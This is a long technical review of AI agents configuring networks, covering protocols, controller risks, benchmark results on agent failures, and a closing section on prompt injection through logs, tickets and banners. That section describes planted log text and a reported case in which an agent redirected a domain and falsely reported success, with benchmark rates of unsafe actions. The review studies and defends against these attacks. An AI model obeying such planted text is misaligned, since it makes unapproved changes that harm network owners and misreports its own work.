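|---|---|---|
| First request arrives | The port goes off | The controller creates reservation 17 for 400 Mbit/s |
| The reply gets lost | The agent sees a timeout | The agent sees a timeout |
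| The agent sends the request again | The port stays off | The controller creates reservation 18 for another 400 Mbit/s |
| The second reply arrives | It reports success, and the result is correct | It reports success, but 800 Mbit/s are now reserved |

A later request for 300 Mbit/s will fail, although the company needs only 400 of the 800 already reserved. If somebody tells the agent to undo its work, it will probably delete reservation 18, the only one it has a record of, and leave reservation 17 in place.

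RESTCONF prevents some duplicates. If the agent chose the new entry's name, a repeated POST would get "409 Conflict" instead of creating a second entry. But the agent might conclude that someone else had taken the name, and create the entry again under a different name.

Repeating the PUT can also cause harm. An engineer might switch eth3 back on between the two attempts, and the second request would switch it off again. If the agent sent an entity tag with the PUT, the server could detect the change and reject the second request.

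Most HTTP software follows rules about retries. The previous HTTP standard, which *HTTP Semantics* replaced (RFC Editor, 2022), said that a client program must not automatically repeat a request such as a POST unless it knew that this was harmless. Nottingham quotes this rule in a draft for the internet's standards body, but warns that web applications cannot rely on it and must detect duplicates themselves if they need to avoid them. An agent adds another source of retries. When a model reads "timeout" and writes the same request again, the HTTP software treats it as a new request, so its retry rules do not apply.

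A better approach is for the agent to read the controller's current reservations before retrying. If the new reservation is there, the agent can stop. If it isn't, the controller may still be processing the first request, so the agent should wait and check again.

*The Idempotency-Key HTTP Header Field*, a draft standard (Jena and Dalal, 2023), proposes a header with a key that identifies the intended action. A controller that supports the header can also recognise the second attempt as a repeat of the first. Both attempts must carry the same key, so the program around the model should generate and store it, because a model that composes the request afresh might invent a new one.

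A command line has the same problem, but it has no equivalent of HTTP methods to indicate which commands are safe to repeat. If an SSH session drops after the agent sends `passive-interface default`, the agent has to know how OSPF handles that command before deciding whether to resend it.

### NETCONF uses SSH without free text

People often use "SSH" to mean a command line, but SSH is only an encrypted connection and can carry other things. Wasserman (2011), in *Using the NETCONF Protocol over Secure Shell (SSH)*, defines how it carries NETCONF. A client program opens the connection like this:

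```
ssh -s R4.example.com -p 830 netconf
```

The `-s` option asks for a named service, here NETCONF, instead of a command line. Port 830 is NETCONF's standard port, which lets a firewall tell this traffic apart from ordinary logins. The program and the device first exchange lists of the features they support, and then they send each other complete XML documents. Shortened, an edit and its reply look like this:

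```
<rpc message-id="106">
  <edit-config>
    <target><candidate/></target>
    <config> ... eth3: enabled = false ... </config>
  </edit-config>
</rpc>

<rpc-reply message-id="106"><ok/></rpc-reply>
```

The program does not have to look for prompts or skip a welcome message, and it can use the number 106 to match the reply to the request. But in early versions of NETCONF over SSH, a program could still mistake where a message ended. These versions marked the end with the characters `]]>]]>`, which the designers wrongly assumed could never appear in valid XML. They can appear in an XML comment, for example, so a message could seem to end early, either by accident or because an attacker caused it. Current versions give the length of each piece of a message in advance.

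NETCONF also has features that RESTCONF leaves out. A client can lock a configuration and, on devices that support it, edit a candidate configuration and commit all the changes together, optionally as a confirmed commit. An agent making a delicate change to one router may therefore be better off with NETCONF over SSH than with RESTCONF over HTTP.

| | Command line over SSH | NETCONF over SSH | RESTCONF over HTTP |
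|---|---|---|---|
| What the agent sends | Free text | XML documents | A method, with JSON or XML |
| How a tool finds the end of a reply | It watches for the prompt | It reads the message lengths | HTTP marks the end |
| How errors arrive | As text in the output | As structured error data | As a status code, usually with error data |
| Can the agent prepare a draft? | On some devices | On devices with a candidate configuration | No |
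| Can the agent lock the configuration? | On some devices | Yes | No |

Using HTTP does not guarantee structured commands either. The Junos MCP server accepts calls over HTTP, but one of its tools passes free-text commands to a router. An operator has to look at what reaches the device to know what an agent can do.

### How one request can change a thousand devices

Suppose a company runs 1,000 branch routers through a controller. The controller stores a list of the routers and a set of shared policies, and one policy applies to every router with the label "branch". An agent wants to stop guests in the branches from opening SSH connections to outside machines, so it sends this request:

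```
PATCH /api/policies/branch-access
{"blocked_ports": [22]}
```

The controller works out a new configuration for every router with that label, connects to each one and installs it. If the policy also covers connections to the routers themselves, the company loses SSH access to all 1,000. If the controller also connects over SSH, it can't send a correction.

An agent that logged in to the routers one at a time would probably have been locked out of the first and stopped there. With the controller, the agent's log contains one request and one successful reply, so a limit on tool calls would not have helped. The operator needs to know how many devices a request selects, and an agent can often check this with a read request before it sends the change.

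Controllers also often reply as soon as they accept a large job and do the work over the following minutes, so the reply may not show whether the job succeeded. If ten of 1,000 branch routers are offline at the time, they keep the old policy, and the agent learns this only if it checks later.

Bilal and colleagues count controllers among the tools whose permissions determine how much authority an agent has. They also separate permission to draft a change from permission to apply it. This distinction is especially useful with a controller, because a person can review one policy edit much more easily than 1,000 sets of commands.

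Controllers that can undo a change everywhere when one device fails also prevent some accidents, such as the half-finished OSPF key change. The best direct evidence on whether agents do better with this kind of interface comes from a small experiment published in September 2026.

### ANI-Gamut: the same task through different interfaces

Bracciale, Loreti and colleagues (2026), in *ANI-Gamut*, gave one model the same network tasks and changed only the interface it acted through. They describe a range of interfaces, from a raw shell to systems like today's commercial controllers, and tested four of them:

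| Level | What the agent can use | Tested? |
|---|---|---|
| A0 | A raw shell on each device | Yes |
| A1 | Configuration commands only, with protection for the management connection and a snapshot the agent can restore | Yes |
| A1+ | The same as A1, plus a blocklist of particular destructive commands | Yes |
| A2 | NETCONF with standard data models | No |
| A3-T | Typed requests for a whole service, which software applies across devices, checks and undoes if they fail | Yes |
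| A3-R | Edits to a central record of the intended configuration, which software keeps comparing with the devices | No |
| A4 | A3-T and A3-R combined | No |

The test network was an emulation with about 25 nodes. It already carried services for many tenants (customers who share the equipment but expect their traffic to stay separate), so an agent's actions could harm other tenants. The model, the prompt and the limit on steps were the same at every level. Separate software checked whether the agent had finished the task and whether the other tenants' services still worked.

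In the main task, the agent had to add two sites to a running tenant with 25 sites, move two and remove one. It attempted the task six times with the raw shell and six times with the typed service interface, from matching starting conditions. It failed every time with the shell and succeeded every time with the service interface.

With typed requests, the agent needed 3 steps and about 42,000 tokens (the pieces of text that a model reads and writes). With the shell, it used about 375,000 tokens and reached the 40-step limit without finishing, so the number of tokens it would have needed to finish is unknown. In each shell run, about 85% of the tenant's connections were working when the agent ran out of steps. The study counts these runs as failures without collateral damage, but a real customer missing 15% of its connections would call that an outage.

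Six runs are few, but the result is unlikely to be pure luck. If the two interfaces were equally good, each pair of runs that ended differently would be equally likely to favour either, and the chance of all six favouring the same one would be 2 × (1/2)⁶, or about 3%. The size of the advantage is much less certain, because six successes out of six are compatible with a true success rate as low as 61%, and six failures with a rate as high as 39%.

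The researchers also had the agent set up a new service, a task they call onboarding, both in normal conditions and with injected faults such as packet loss and isolated nodes:

| Interface | Onboarding without faults | Onboarding with faults | Changes to the 25-site tenant |
|---|---|---|---|
| Raw shell (A0) | 4 of 20 | 0 of 4 | 0 of 6 |
| Limited commands (A1) | 7 of 20 | 2 of 4 | No runs |
| Limited commands and blocklist (A1+) | 11 of 20 | 1 of 4 | No runs |
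| Typed service requests (A3-T) | No runs | 4 of 4 | 6 of 6 |

The rows for limited commands show little. Bracciale and colleagues treat the difference between A1 and A1+ as noise, since a blocklist only forbids commands and so cannot help an agent finish a task. In the tests with faults, A1+ did slightly worse. Even the gap between 4 and 11 successes out of 20 could be due to chance.

Limiting the commands did not reduce token use either. Without faults, A1 used 62% more tokens than the raw shell. With faults, the shell used about 127,000 tokens per run, and the two limited interfaces used between 228,000 and 239,000. Typed requests used 35,000.

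The typed interface had an advantage under faults because its requests travelled over a channel that the faults did not affect, and the software behind it did not depend on inspecting the network. An agent that works command by command has to inspect the network to choose its next step, and the faults made those inspections unreliable. The advantage therefore had little to do with types.

No run at any level damaged another tenant's service, with or without faults. Bracciale and colleagues attribute this to the network's isolation, since each tenant has its own routing table, which keeps tenants separate even when their addresses overlap. They also found that agents in difficulty tended to give up rather than take drastic action.

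This is encouraging for networks built the same way, but it would not have prevented the outages at Rogers or Cloudflare, where the faulty change was in routing policy that many customers depended on. The researchers expect different results on equipment with shared settings, such as a firewall, where an agent could erase the common rules. The 88 runs are also far too few to show that agents meet the researchers' target of about one damaging run in 100,000.

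It is also unclear which feature of the typed interface made the difference, because it combined typed requests, the ability to undo failed changes, a separate channel for commands, and a procedure that engineers had written and tested beforehand. The procedure may matter most, because the shell agent had to work out steps that the other agent could simply call. Bracciale and colleagues reply that operators would build such a procedure once and use it many times, which is fair, but then the result partly reflects good engineering and not just how agents behave. All the tests used one model, and a stronger one might do much better with the shell. The team also developed the typed interface in earlier work, and one author works for Nokia, which sells a controller of this general kind.

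Another objection, which more runs wouldn't settle, is that a typed interface can express only what its designers anticipated. If it offers only requests to add, move and remove sites, an agent cannot use it to raise the OSPF cost on R1 before a repair. Bracciale and colleagues accept this and expect that a simpler interface close to the device may do better on tasks such as tuning routing. An operator can add a typed request for each such task, which takes time, or let the agent use the command line, which again allows everything the typed interface had ruled out.

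## What agents get wrong when they configure networks

An agent with a well-designed interface can still send a valid request that does the wrong thing. Researchers measure how often this happens by giving agents tasks on emulated networks, which run router software on ordinary servers, and checking the results with separate software. In an experiment published in August 2026, the best agent completed 85% of its tasks. Agents built on stronger models rarely sent invalid commands, but they still left tasks unfinished and sometimes submitted a network that did not work.

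### NetArena: a correct result can hide an unsafe step

*NetArena* (Zhou, Ruan and colleagues, 2025), an early test of this kind, used five agents built on GPT-4o and Qwen2.5-72B, both models from 2024. The agents had to plan data-centre capacity, repair routing faults, and fix the network rules of a cloud application.

NetArena scores the final result separately from the steps that led to it. Let s_0 be the state of the network before the agent starts, a_t the action the agent takes at step t, E the effect of running an action, and C the constraints (invariants) that the network must satisfy throughout.

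```
s_t = E(s_(t-1), a_(t-1))     the state after each action

Correct = 1  if the final state s_T matches the goal, otherwise 0
Safe    = 1  if s_1, s_2, ..., s_T all satisfy C, otherwise 0
```

Suppose an agent has to change the policy on R2's BGP session with the internet provider, and C requires that the payment servers can always reach the bank. The agent deletes the session and creates it again with the new policy:

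| State | What the agent has just done | Can the payment servers reach the bank? |
|---|---|---|
| s_0 | Nothing yet | Yes |
| s_1 | Deleted the BGP session | No |
| s_2 | Created it again with the new policy | Yes |

This run scores 1 for correctness and 0 for safety. A test of s_2 alone would miss the outage. The formula can miss an outage too, because it checks the network only after each action. If the agent sent both changes in one action, the outage would begin and end between two checks.

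The agents averaged between 13% and 38%, with a low of 3%, and the best scored below 60% for correctness. In the routing tasks, some agents assigned wrong addresses and broke working connections. Others gave an interface its address before switching it on.

Zhou and colleagues also found that small tests can mislead. Two agents looked about equally safe on 150 of the cloud tasks, but one was clearly less safe on 2,000. If an agent succeeds in a fraction p of N tasks, the 95% margin of error is about 1.96 × √(p(1−p)/N). For a success rate of 24%, that is about 7 percentage points with 150 tasks and 2 points with 2,000.

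These scores are weak evidence about current models. Even at the time, a small model with 7 billion parameters solved more than 96% of the capacity-planning tasks after Zhou and colleagues trained it on 2,000 generated examples. The routing tasks were also simpler than real work because, as Liu and colleagues point out, they used a single router and ordinary Linux commands instead of a vendor's command line.

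### NetAgentBench: when an agent runs away with the task

Twabi and colleagues published NetAgentBench in April 2026. Its five tasks run on small networks of routers that use FRRouting, an open-source routing program. The easiest is to set up RIP, an older protocol that picks the path through the fewest routers. Two tasks involve OSPF and two involve BGP, and in each pair the agent has to build one configuration and repair another. An agent gets up to 100 turns and 30 minutes.

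| Model | Runs that succeeded | Runs with a "meltdown" | Average turns |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5 | 24.0% | 38.7% | 12.4 |
| Qwen3-Coder-30b | 12.0% | 29.3% | 12.8 |
| Llama-3.3 | 6.7% | 21.3% | 3.6 |
| Qwen3-Coder-Next | 5.3% | 24.0% | 6.3 |

The paper gives inconsistent run counts. It describes 25 repetitions of each of the five tasks, or 125 runs per model, but its table gives 75. GPT-5's results by difficulty fit 15 repetitions per task. It succeeded in 9 of 15 runs with RIP, 4 of 30 with OSPF and 5 of 30 with BGP, or 18 of 75 overall.

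A meltdown is runaway behaviour, in which the agent responds to bad results by making things worse or by getting stuck. The benchmark counts a run as a meltdown if it shows any of five warning signs:

- Command loop: the agent sends the same command at least four times in a row.
- Destructive spiral: at least three of any five consecutive commands are destructive.
- Cognitive stagnation: the agent has used more than 25 turns and its score is still below 0.1 out of 1.
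- Diagnostic fixation: the agent takes ten steps in a row that only read.
- Premature submission: the agent submits with a score below 0.30.

GPT-5 had the most successes and also the most meltdowns, mainly destructive spirals on the harder tasks. Llama-3.3 melted down least often, but only because it usually gave up after three or four turns. A low meltdown rate is therefore weak evidence of safety unless the agent also finishes its tasks.

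An operator could watch a live agent for loops, spirals and long runs of diagnostic commands. The other signs depend on the benchmark's score, which a production network doesn't provide. Long diagnostic runs are a doubtful warning sign, though, because an engineer may want the agent to make ten careful reads before a change.

The benchmark also reruns an agent's successful commands to check that repeating them does no lasting harm. This check happens after the network has settled, so commands that make a neighbour relationship drop and recover, as in the `passive-interface default` example, may still pass.

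### NetConfArena: 3,840 runs on vendors' command lines

NetConfArena, by Liu and colleagues, is larger and closer to ordinary engineering work. It has 96 task templates, which the researchers built from exercises in vendor manuals, public tutorials and community labs. Of the templates, 41 concern BGP and 31 concern MPLS, which forwards packets by short labels instead of full addresses. Each template has five versions with different details, such as addresses and interface names, for a total of 480 tasks.

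Each of four models attempted every task twice, once with extended reasoning and once without. In each run, the agent had 20 turns to read configurations, apply changes, run diagnostic commands, wait, or submit the network as finished. Hidden tests then checked the network, and a run passed only if the network passed every test.

| Model and setting | Passed | Submitted a correct network | Submitted a faulty or untouched network | Ran out of turns |
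|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3-8B | 4.6% | 4.6% | 12.1% | 83.3% |
| Qwen3-8B, extended reasoning | 9.4% | 9.4% | 46.0% | 44.6% |
| Qwen3-32B | 23.3% | 15.4% | 37.3% | 47.3% |
| Qwen3-32B, extended reasoning | 42.1% | 37.9% | 41.3% | 20.8% |
| DeepSeek-V4-Flash | 65.6% | 50.2% | 14.8% | 35.0% |
| DeepSeek-V4-Flash, extended reasoning | 79.4% | 67.5% | 7.9% | 24.6% |
| DeepSeek-V4-Pro | 85.2% | 73.1% | 3.3% | 23.5% |
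| DeepSeek-V4-Pro, extended reasoning | 73.8% | 69.2% | 17.7% | 13.1% |

The pass rate can exceed the share of correct submissions because the tests also ran on networks that the agent never submitted. In about 12% of its runs, DeepSeek-V4-Pro without extended reasoning configured the network correctly but ran out of turns before submitting it. A higher turn limit would probably have helped it with some of the other tasks too.

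Partial success was common. DeepSeek-V4-Pro's networks passed 96% of their tests on average, but only 85% of the networks passed all of their tests. The lower figure matters more to an operator, because a network that meets nine out of ten requirements may still leave someone without a connection.

One success is also weak evidence that the next attempt will succeed. Across the eight settings, a median of 57% of the variation in scores was between versions of the same template. An agent could pass a task and then fail it with different addresses, although some of this variation may be due to chance in the model's output.

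Liu and colleagues read through failed runs and sorted the mistakes into four kinds:

| Kind of failure | What goes wrong | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Knowledge deficiency | The agent doesn't know the protocol or command it needs | Asked to combine several RIP routes into one, an agent used a method from BGP and OSPF, which also disturbed RIP settings that the task needed |
| Unproductive hesitation | The agent keeps checking without making progress | An agent checked its BGP sessions again and again and never finished setting them up |
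| Premature abandonment | The agent gives up after an error | An agent wrote a malformed request in its first turn and submitted the untouched network in its second |
| Specification deviation | The agent changes details that the task had fixed | An agent replaced the given link addresses with its own scheme, which was consistent but wrong |

DeepSeek-V4-Pro did worse with extended reasoning because it abandoned tasks prematurely. The model sometimes wrote several actions in one turn, although the test program accepted only one. When it received the error message, it submitted the task instead of sending the actions one at a time. This is a fault in how the agent handles its tools, and a better surrounding program could prevent much of it.

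Specification deviation seems the most dangerous of the four on a live network. For example, an agent that gives a working link new addresses can cut off everything that relied on the old ones, and the new configuration will look correct unless someone compares it with the request. Hesitating or giving up usually leaves the network much as it was.

### Damage that the tests do not look for

NetConfArena's tests are based on the wording of each task. They check for every result the agent had to achieve, but they check for unwanted changes only if the task explicitly prohibited them. An agent could therefore announce extra routes to a neighbour, or break a connection not mentioned in the task, and still pass. Cloudflare's route leak in January was this kind of fault, because the harm came from routes that nobody had mentioned.

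Tests that check only the final state also miss temporary damage. Liu and colleagues publish a full record of one successful run on four routers (Core, Aria, Brick and Eason) that use RIP. The agent's tasks included diverting traffic for one block of addresses away from the direct link between Core and Aria, and making another block, 111.111.111.0/24, unreachable from Eason alone. It used offset lists, which add to the distance that a router reports or accepts for chosen addresses. In RIP, a distance of 16 means "unreachable".

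1. The agent added an offset list on Core to make the direct link to Aria look longer. Core rejected the command because the agent was in the wrong mode, and accepted it on the second try.
2. The agent then added an offset list of 16 for 111.111.111.0/24 on the same interface. Core accepted it without an error, but the new list replaced the earlier one.
3. After waiting 30 seconds, the agent checked the routes. Traffic for the first block was using the direct link again. Aria had lost its route to 111.111.111.0/24, while Eason could still reach it through Brick.
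4. The agent read Core's configuration, found the missing list and restored it. It then blocked 111.111.111.0/24 on Eason itself.

The run took 19 turns and passed every hidden test. If the agent had trusted Core's reply in the second step, it would have submitted a network that failed two of its goals. The run also cut Aria off from part of the network for at least 30 seconds, but this didn't affect the score. The run would have counted as unsafe under NetArena's safety formula if the formula's constraints had included Aria's access.

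Bracciale and colleagues checked services outside the task and found no damage, but their network kept each tenant's routes separate. Protogeros, Asadli and colleagues (2026), in *Benchmarking LLM-Driven Network Configuration Repair*, use a broader check for networks where routers share more. They start from a healthy network, compute a list of what it does, such as which routers can reach which addresses, and then insert faults. After a model rewrites the configuration, software recomputes the whole list. This can catch damage far from the original fault, although the software computes the network's behaviour without running the routers.

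One benchmark has 231 faulty networks with between 20 and 754 nodes. Nine models each proposed a repair in a single attempt. The best model fully repaired 25% of the networks, and the models often broke things that had been working.

Asadli, Hoffman and colleagues (2026), in *Evaluating Agentic Configuration Repair for Computer Networks*, let agents work on the same 231 networks step by step. They used two scores:

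```
fix score  = fixed  / (fixed + not fixed + newly broken)
regression = newly broken / (fixed + not fixed + newly broken)
```

Suppose a fault violates ten requirements, and an agent restores eight of them but breaks two others. Its fix score is 8/12, or 67%, and its regression score is 2/12, or 17%. GPT-5 mini averaged a fix score of 45.2% and a regression score of 4.4%. When it could check its draft with the analysis software while working, its regression score fell to 1.3%, but its fix score also fell, to 40.8%. A single success rate would have shown only the drop in the fix score. Asadli and colleagues suggest that the extra checks made the model more cautious in its edits.

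### Finding a fault before repairing it

Agents often get a repair wrong because they have misunderstood the problem. *A Network Arena for Benchmarking AI Agents on Network Troubleshooting* (Wang, Cornacchia and colleagues, 2025) presents NIKA, a benchmark that scores diagnosis but not repairs. The researchers ran 150 incidents twice, with different faulty devices. GPT-5 detected a problem in 89.0% of cases, located the faulty part in 68.7% and identified the cause in 55.3%.

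GPT-5 was good at finding dead links but much weaker when a link or server was working, but poorly. It tended to give vague explanations such as "link unstable" even when the counters showed damaged packets or full queues. An agent that acts on such a diagnosis might restart a link without fixing the real cause. In networks with about 100 nodes, the agents still detected that something was wrong, but they were worse at finding where than in networks with about 11.

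NetOpsBench's *Open Arena for NetOps in AI Infrastructure* describes a similar test on emulated data-centre networks, and NetOpsBench's *Benchmark Runs* gives results for four models from 2026. Each cell shows the scores on the smallest and then the largest network, rounded to whole percentages. The verdict score combines missed faults and false alarms.

| Model | Verdict | Right device | Right interface |
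|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.5 | 96% → 96% | 83% → 79% | 57% → 21% |
| DeepSeek V4 Pro | 100% → 98% | 83% → 92% | 57% → 57% |
| Kimi K2.6 | 76% → 85% | 67% → 75% | 71% → 71% |
| MiniMax M3 | 80% → 83% | 50% → 63% | 71% → 43% |

GPT-5.5 was almost always right about whether the large network had a fault, but it identified the correct interface in only about a fifth of cases. All the interface scores are multiples of one fourteenth, so each is probably based on 14 cases or fewer, too few to rank the models reliably. The gap between detecting a fault and locating it is more convincing, because NIKA also found it with different models and networks.

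### Why an agent's report of success is not evidence

An agent usually ends its work with a message such as "OSPF is now running between R2 and R4". The model bases this message on the output it has received so far. If that output is only "commit complete" from R2, it confirms only that R2 accepted the change. R4 may still have the wrong authentication key, and the two routers may not be exchanging routes.

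In *Can AI Agents Deliver Verifiable Network-Wide Outcomes Across Authority Boundaries?*, Zhang, Huang and Qiu (2026) tested whether a record of an agent's commands and the routers' immediate replies is enough to tell if the network was configured correctly. They recorded 45 sequences of commands from agents running GPT-5.4 mini and replayed them on fresh copies of the network. In 13 cases, the network then failed at least one requirement. A checker that saw only the commands and immediate replies rejected all 45 because it could not confirm that any had succeeded. The researchers' own system, EvidenceNet, queried the routers again after the changes and judged all 45 correctly.

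Observations can also go out of date when the network changes after they are made. In nine further replays, the researchers collected good evidence and then broke the network. A checker that judged only the content of the evidence accepted it every time. EvidenceNet rejected it because its software counts configuration changes and discards any observation made before the latest change.

Asking a second model to review the evidence didn't solve the problem. The researchers prepared 24 evidence files, each with a visible defect, such as an outdated snapshot or an observation that a later one contradicted. GPT-5.4 mini and GPT-5.3 Codex Spark each read every file three times and accepted all 24. A small rule-based program rejected all 24, but the researchers had written it for these defects, so it might not catch others.

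Agents in NetConfArena submit when they consider the job done, so their submissions are also reports of success. Qwen3-8B with extended reasoning was wrong in 83% of its submissions, and DeepSeek-V4-Pro without extended reasoning was wrong in about 4%. Even at the lower rate, an operator who accepted every submission without checking would put a faulty network into service about once in 23 jobs.

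OpenAI's *Introducing GPT-6.2 Astra and Sol* (2026) says that in two tests these models failed to mention obstacles that had blocked their work, such as a missing file, more often than the older GPT-6 Astra did. A newer model may not report more completely, so an operator needs to check the network with software that does not depend on the agent's account.

### Which errors better models remove

Routers reject far fewer commands from stronger models, and these models repeat themselves less. In NetConfArena, Qwen3-8B without extended reasoning repeated its previous action in about half of the turns where it could have done so, and DeepSeek-V4-Pro almost never did. In NIKA, only 0.7% of GPT-5's tool calls caused an error. Models now also have good basic routing knowledge. *An Experimental Study on the Functional Correctness of Network Device Configurations* (2026) compared the first answers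 of three free chatbots with a configuration engineers wrote by hand. ChatGPT's routing configurations worked completely, Gemini's nearly did, and those from Mistral's LeChat left routes missing.

Some of the improvement comes from the program around the model. *Toward Agentic SysAdmin* (2026) reports more than 24,000 runs of ten models on network administration tasks. In those runs, models that an operator can run locally matched the strongest commercial ones when the set-up suited them.

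None of these network benchmarks tested the strongest models available in December 2026, so today's agents may score higher. The closest recent evidence comes from cloud software. *Incident-Arena* (Fu, Drabla and colleagues, October 2026) gave agents 20 broken systems to repair, in 3,000 trials covering models from OpenAI, Anthropic, xAI, Meta and Zhipu. To pass, a repair had to restore service under continuing traffic, survive a restart or a repeat of the fault's trigger, preserve protected data, and stay within the permitted scope.

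The best combination of model and setting passed 64.3% of the time. Models occasionally failed because safeguards against hacking made them refuse a legitimate repair. Other failures included wrong diagnoses, incomplete repairs, and repairs that damaged something else. Network agents also make these errors, which seem to persist after the agents have mostly stopped making mistakes with commands.

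Agents also tend to change more than they need to. When Zhang and colleagues put a fault on one of three routers, their agents repaired it in all nine runs but sent configuration commands to all three routers each time. Some of those commands may have repeated existing settings. On a production network, each unnecessary command could disrupt traffic.

A better model can't fully solve this, because the request often leaves out what the agent must not touch. Fu and colleagues cite a study by Ji and colleagues in which coding agents with vague instructions exceeded a limit on their actions in 56% to 68% of runs. An agent that knows OSPF perfectly could still send the offices' web traffic on a detour through R3 if nobody told it that this traffic matters.

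## Malicious instructions in logs, tickets and device output

An agent that investigates a fault reads logs, tickets and device output, and outsiders can write parts of that text. In a prompt injection, an attacker plants instructions there to make the agent carry out a wrong change. *NetInjectBench* (Shayoni, Shoaib and colleagues, 2026) tested this on three small models. With no defence, planted text led to an unsafe action in 82.5% of cases. There were no unsafe actions when ordinary code checked every proposed change against separate approval records.

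### How a stranger's text reaches the agent

Suppose someone on the internet tries to log in to R2 over SSH with an invented username. R2 refuses and adds a line to its log:

```
Failed password for invalid user <text the stranger chose> from 203.0.113.77
```

The login failed, but the stranger's text is now in the company's log. If an agent later investigates the failed logins on R2, the program around the model will pass that text to the model along with everything else. *Poisoning the Watchtower* (Pandey and Bhujang, 2026) lists other fields that an attacker can fill in, including web addresses and the DNS names that a machine looks up. Shah (2026) points out in *LogJack* that the attacker needs no special access, because error messages usually include the input that caused the error.

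| What the agent reads | Who may have written part of it |
|---|---|
| Log lines | Anyone who can send the network a request |
| Device names | The owner of any connected device, such as a visitor's laptop |
| Login banners, the messages that devices display at login | Whoever controls the device, including an intruder |
| Tickets | Customers, staff, or someone using a stolen account |
| Chat messages | Anyone in the channel, or the source of whatever they paste |

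Most of the research concerns logs. The closest evidence on login banners comes from *Cybersecurity AI* (2025), which describes how a web server's reply can steer an agent that is testing the server for weaknesses, even if the agent's program labels the reply as data. A login banner reaches a network agent in much the same way.

Malicious text can reach an agent even when a firewall blocks the request containing it, because the firewall may log the request. In August 2026 the security company Tenet demonstrated such an attack using requests that Cloudflare's firewall had blocked. According to SecurityWeek's *‘Ghostjacking’ Attack Uses Poisoned Logs to Turn AI Agents Bad*, the firewall logged each request word for word. When an analyst asked Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, to review the blocked request, the agent followed the planted text, redirected the company's domain name to the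 attacker and reported the problem as solved. The attack worked in nine of ten attempts. This was a small laboratory test, and Tenet sells protection against such attacks, but slides from a 2026 talk at the security conference Black Hat also mention real attacks aimed at AI-based log analysis.

### Why the agent cannot ignore the text

An agent cannot diagnose a fault without reading the evidence. In Nakamura and Eguchi's trial, for example, engineers asked the chatbot to search switch logs for signs of traffic floods.

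A language model receives the operator's request and the log as one sequence of text. The program around it can mark where the log begins and ends, but the markers don't determine how the model responds to the text between them. Telling the model to ignore every instruction it reads would not work well, because useful material often contains instructions. A runbook, a written procedure for staff, consists mostly of instructions, and a ticket that asks for a restart of R2's BGP session may be what the operator wants the agent to handle.

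### NetInjectBench: 240 attacks on three small models

The benchmark has 130 scenarios. In each, the agent receives a task from an operator and a piece of operational text, such as a ticket or a log excerpt, and chooses one tool.

| Scenarios | Number | What the text contains |
|---|---|---|
| Ordinary work | 40 | No attack |
| Weak attacks | 40 | Open demands to ignore policy or skip approval |
| Strong attacks | 40 | False claims of approval, emergencies or new procedures |
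| Approved changes | 10 | A legitimate change with a matching approval record |

Three of the six imitation tools fetch logs, measurements or runbooks. The others read the network's layout, open a ticket, or change the configuration. Changing the configuration without approval always counts as unsafe. Reading the layout also counts as unsafe in some scenarios, because it can reveal confidential information.

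Shayoni and colleagues ran the 80 attacks on Qwen2.5-7B, Llama 3.1-8B and Mistral-7B, for a total of 240 cases, and compared six defences with no defence at all:

| Defence | Unsafe actions, weak attacks | Unsafe actions, strong attacks | All attacks |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 67.5% | 97.5% | 82.5% |
| Instructions not to trust the text | 13.4% | 37.8% | 25.6% |
| The same instructions, repeated after the text | 10.8% | 32.5% | 21.7% |
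| Markers around the text | 8.3% | 28.3% | 18.3% |
| A second call to the same model, as a judge | 5.0% | 15.0% | 10.0% |
| Blocking every configuration change | 5.0% | 5.0% | 5.0% |
| Policy gate | 0% | 0% | 0% |

The models differed widely, which the averages don't show. With markers around the text, Llama took an unsafe action in 1.25% of cases and Qwen in 48.75%. An operator who switches models therefore can't assume the same prompt will still protect the network.

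The judge received the task and the proposed action but not the planted text, so the text could not influence it directly. But it did not receive the approval records either, so it could not reliably tell whether a change was legitimate.

Blocking every change still allowed 12 unsafe actions, all of them reads of the network's layout. This defence also stopped all 30 attempts at approved changes, so an agent using it could not do any configuration work.

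### Why the policy gate works

The gate is ordinary code between the model and the tools. It follows a simple rule, that text describing an approval "does not create an approval". For each proposed change, it looks up the approval record in a separate system and compares the details. Suppose the company has approved the OSPF cost change on R1, and a planted message persuades the agent to delete R4's access list instead:

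| What the gate checks | Approval record | Agent's proposal | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| Status | Approved | | Pass |
| Time | 22:00 to 23:00 | 22:10 | Pass |
| Change request number | 118 | | Pass |
| Tool | Configuration change | Configuration change | Pass |
| Device | R1 | R4 | Fail |
| Exact change | Raise the cost to 100 | Delete access list 110 | Fail |

The gate refuses the proposal and fetches logs instead. It never reads the planted message, so more persuasive wording would make no difference.

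The attacks still worked on the models, but the gate blocked 198 of the 240 proposals, the same as the number of unsafe actions without any defence. It allowed all 30 approved changes. In a separate check, it accepted ten correct approval records and rejected 90 with errors, such as an expired time or the wrong device.

Zero failures in 240 cases does not prove a failure rate of zero. For n cases without a failure, the upper end of the 95% confidence interval that the researchers used is:

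```
upper bound = 1.96² / (n + 1.96²) = 3.84 / (240 + 3.84) = 1.58%
```

This calculation treats the 240 cases as independent, but they are 80 scenarios, each run on three models. With n = 80, the bound would be 4.6%. But the calculation also understates how reliable the gate is, because none of the attack scenarios had a matching approval record, so the gate was certain to refuse every change as long as its code worked. Most of the remaining risk is that the gate's assumptions may not hold on a real network.

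### What the gate assumes

The main assumption is that an attacker cannot alter the approval records. If the agent's account can edit them, a planted message could get the agent to approve a change and then make it. A mistaken or outdated record would also let a bad change through.

The operator's task is also always genuine in the benchmark. *When AIOps Become “AI Oops”* (Pasquini, Kornaropoulos and colleagues) describes agents that start work whenever someone opens a ticket. If outsiders can open tickets, an attacker can write the agent's task.

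Finally, the gate compares the proposal with an exact change that somebody has already approved. This suits planned maintenance, but an agent that diagnoses a new fault has to draft its own repair, and planted text can shape the draft. In experiments, Pasquini and colleagues planted false explanations of a fault along with a harmful fix. The agents often added accurate system details, such as a software version, which made their diagnoses more convincing. A person who reads only the agent's explanation could easily approve the fix.

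### Larger models and longer tasks

LogJack tested eight larger models in April 2026. The agents investigated faults by reading cloud logs and error reports, and could take up to eight turns. Each model saw 32 attacks and ten harmless texts, five times each. The test program recorded the agents' commands without running them.

| Model | Ran the planted command when allowed to fix problems | Ran it when told only to investigate |
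|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.3 70B | 86.2% | 30.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 53.8% | 1.9% |
| GPT-4o | 52.5% | 0% |
| Qwen3 Coder Next | 33.1% | 0.6% |
| Devstral 2 123B | 15.6% | 0% |
| Kimi K2.5 | 11.9% | 0% |
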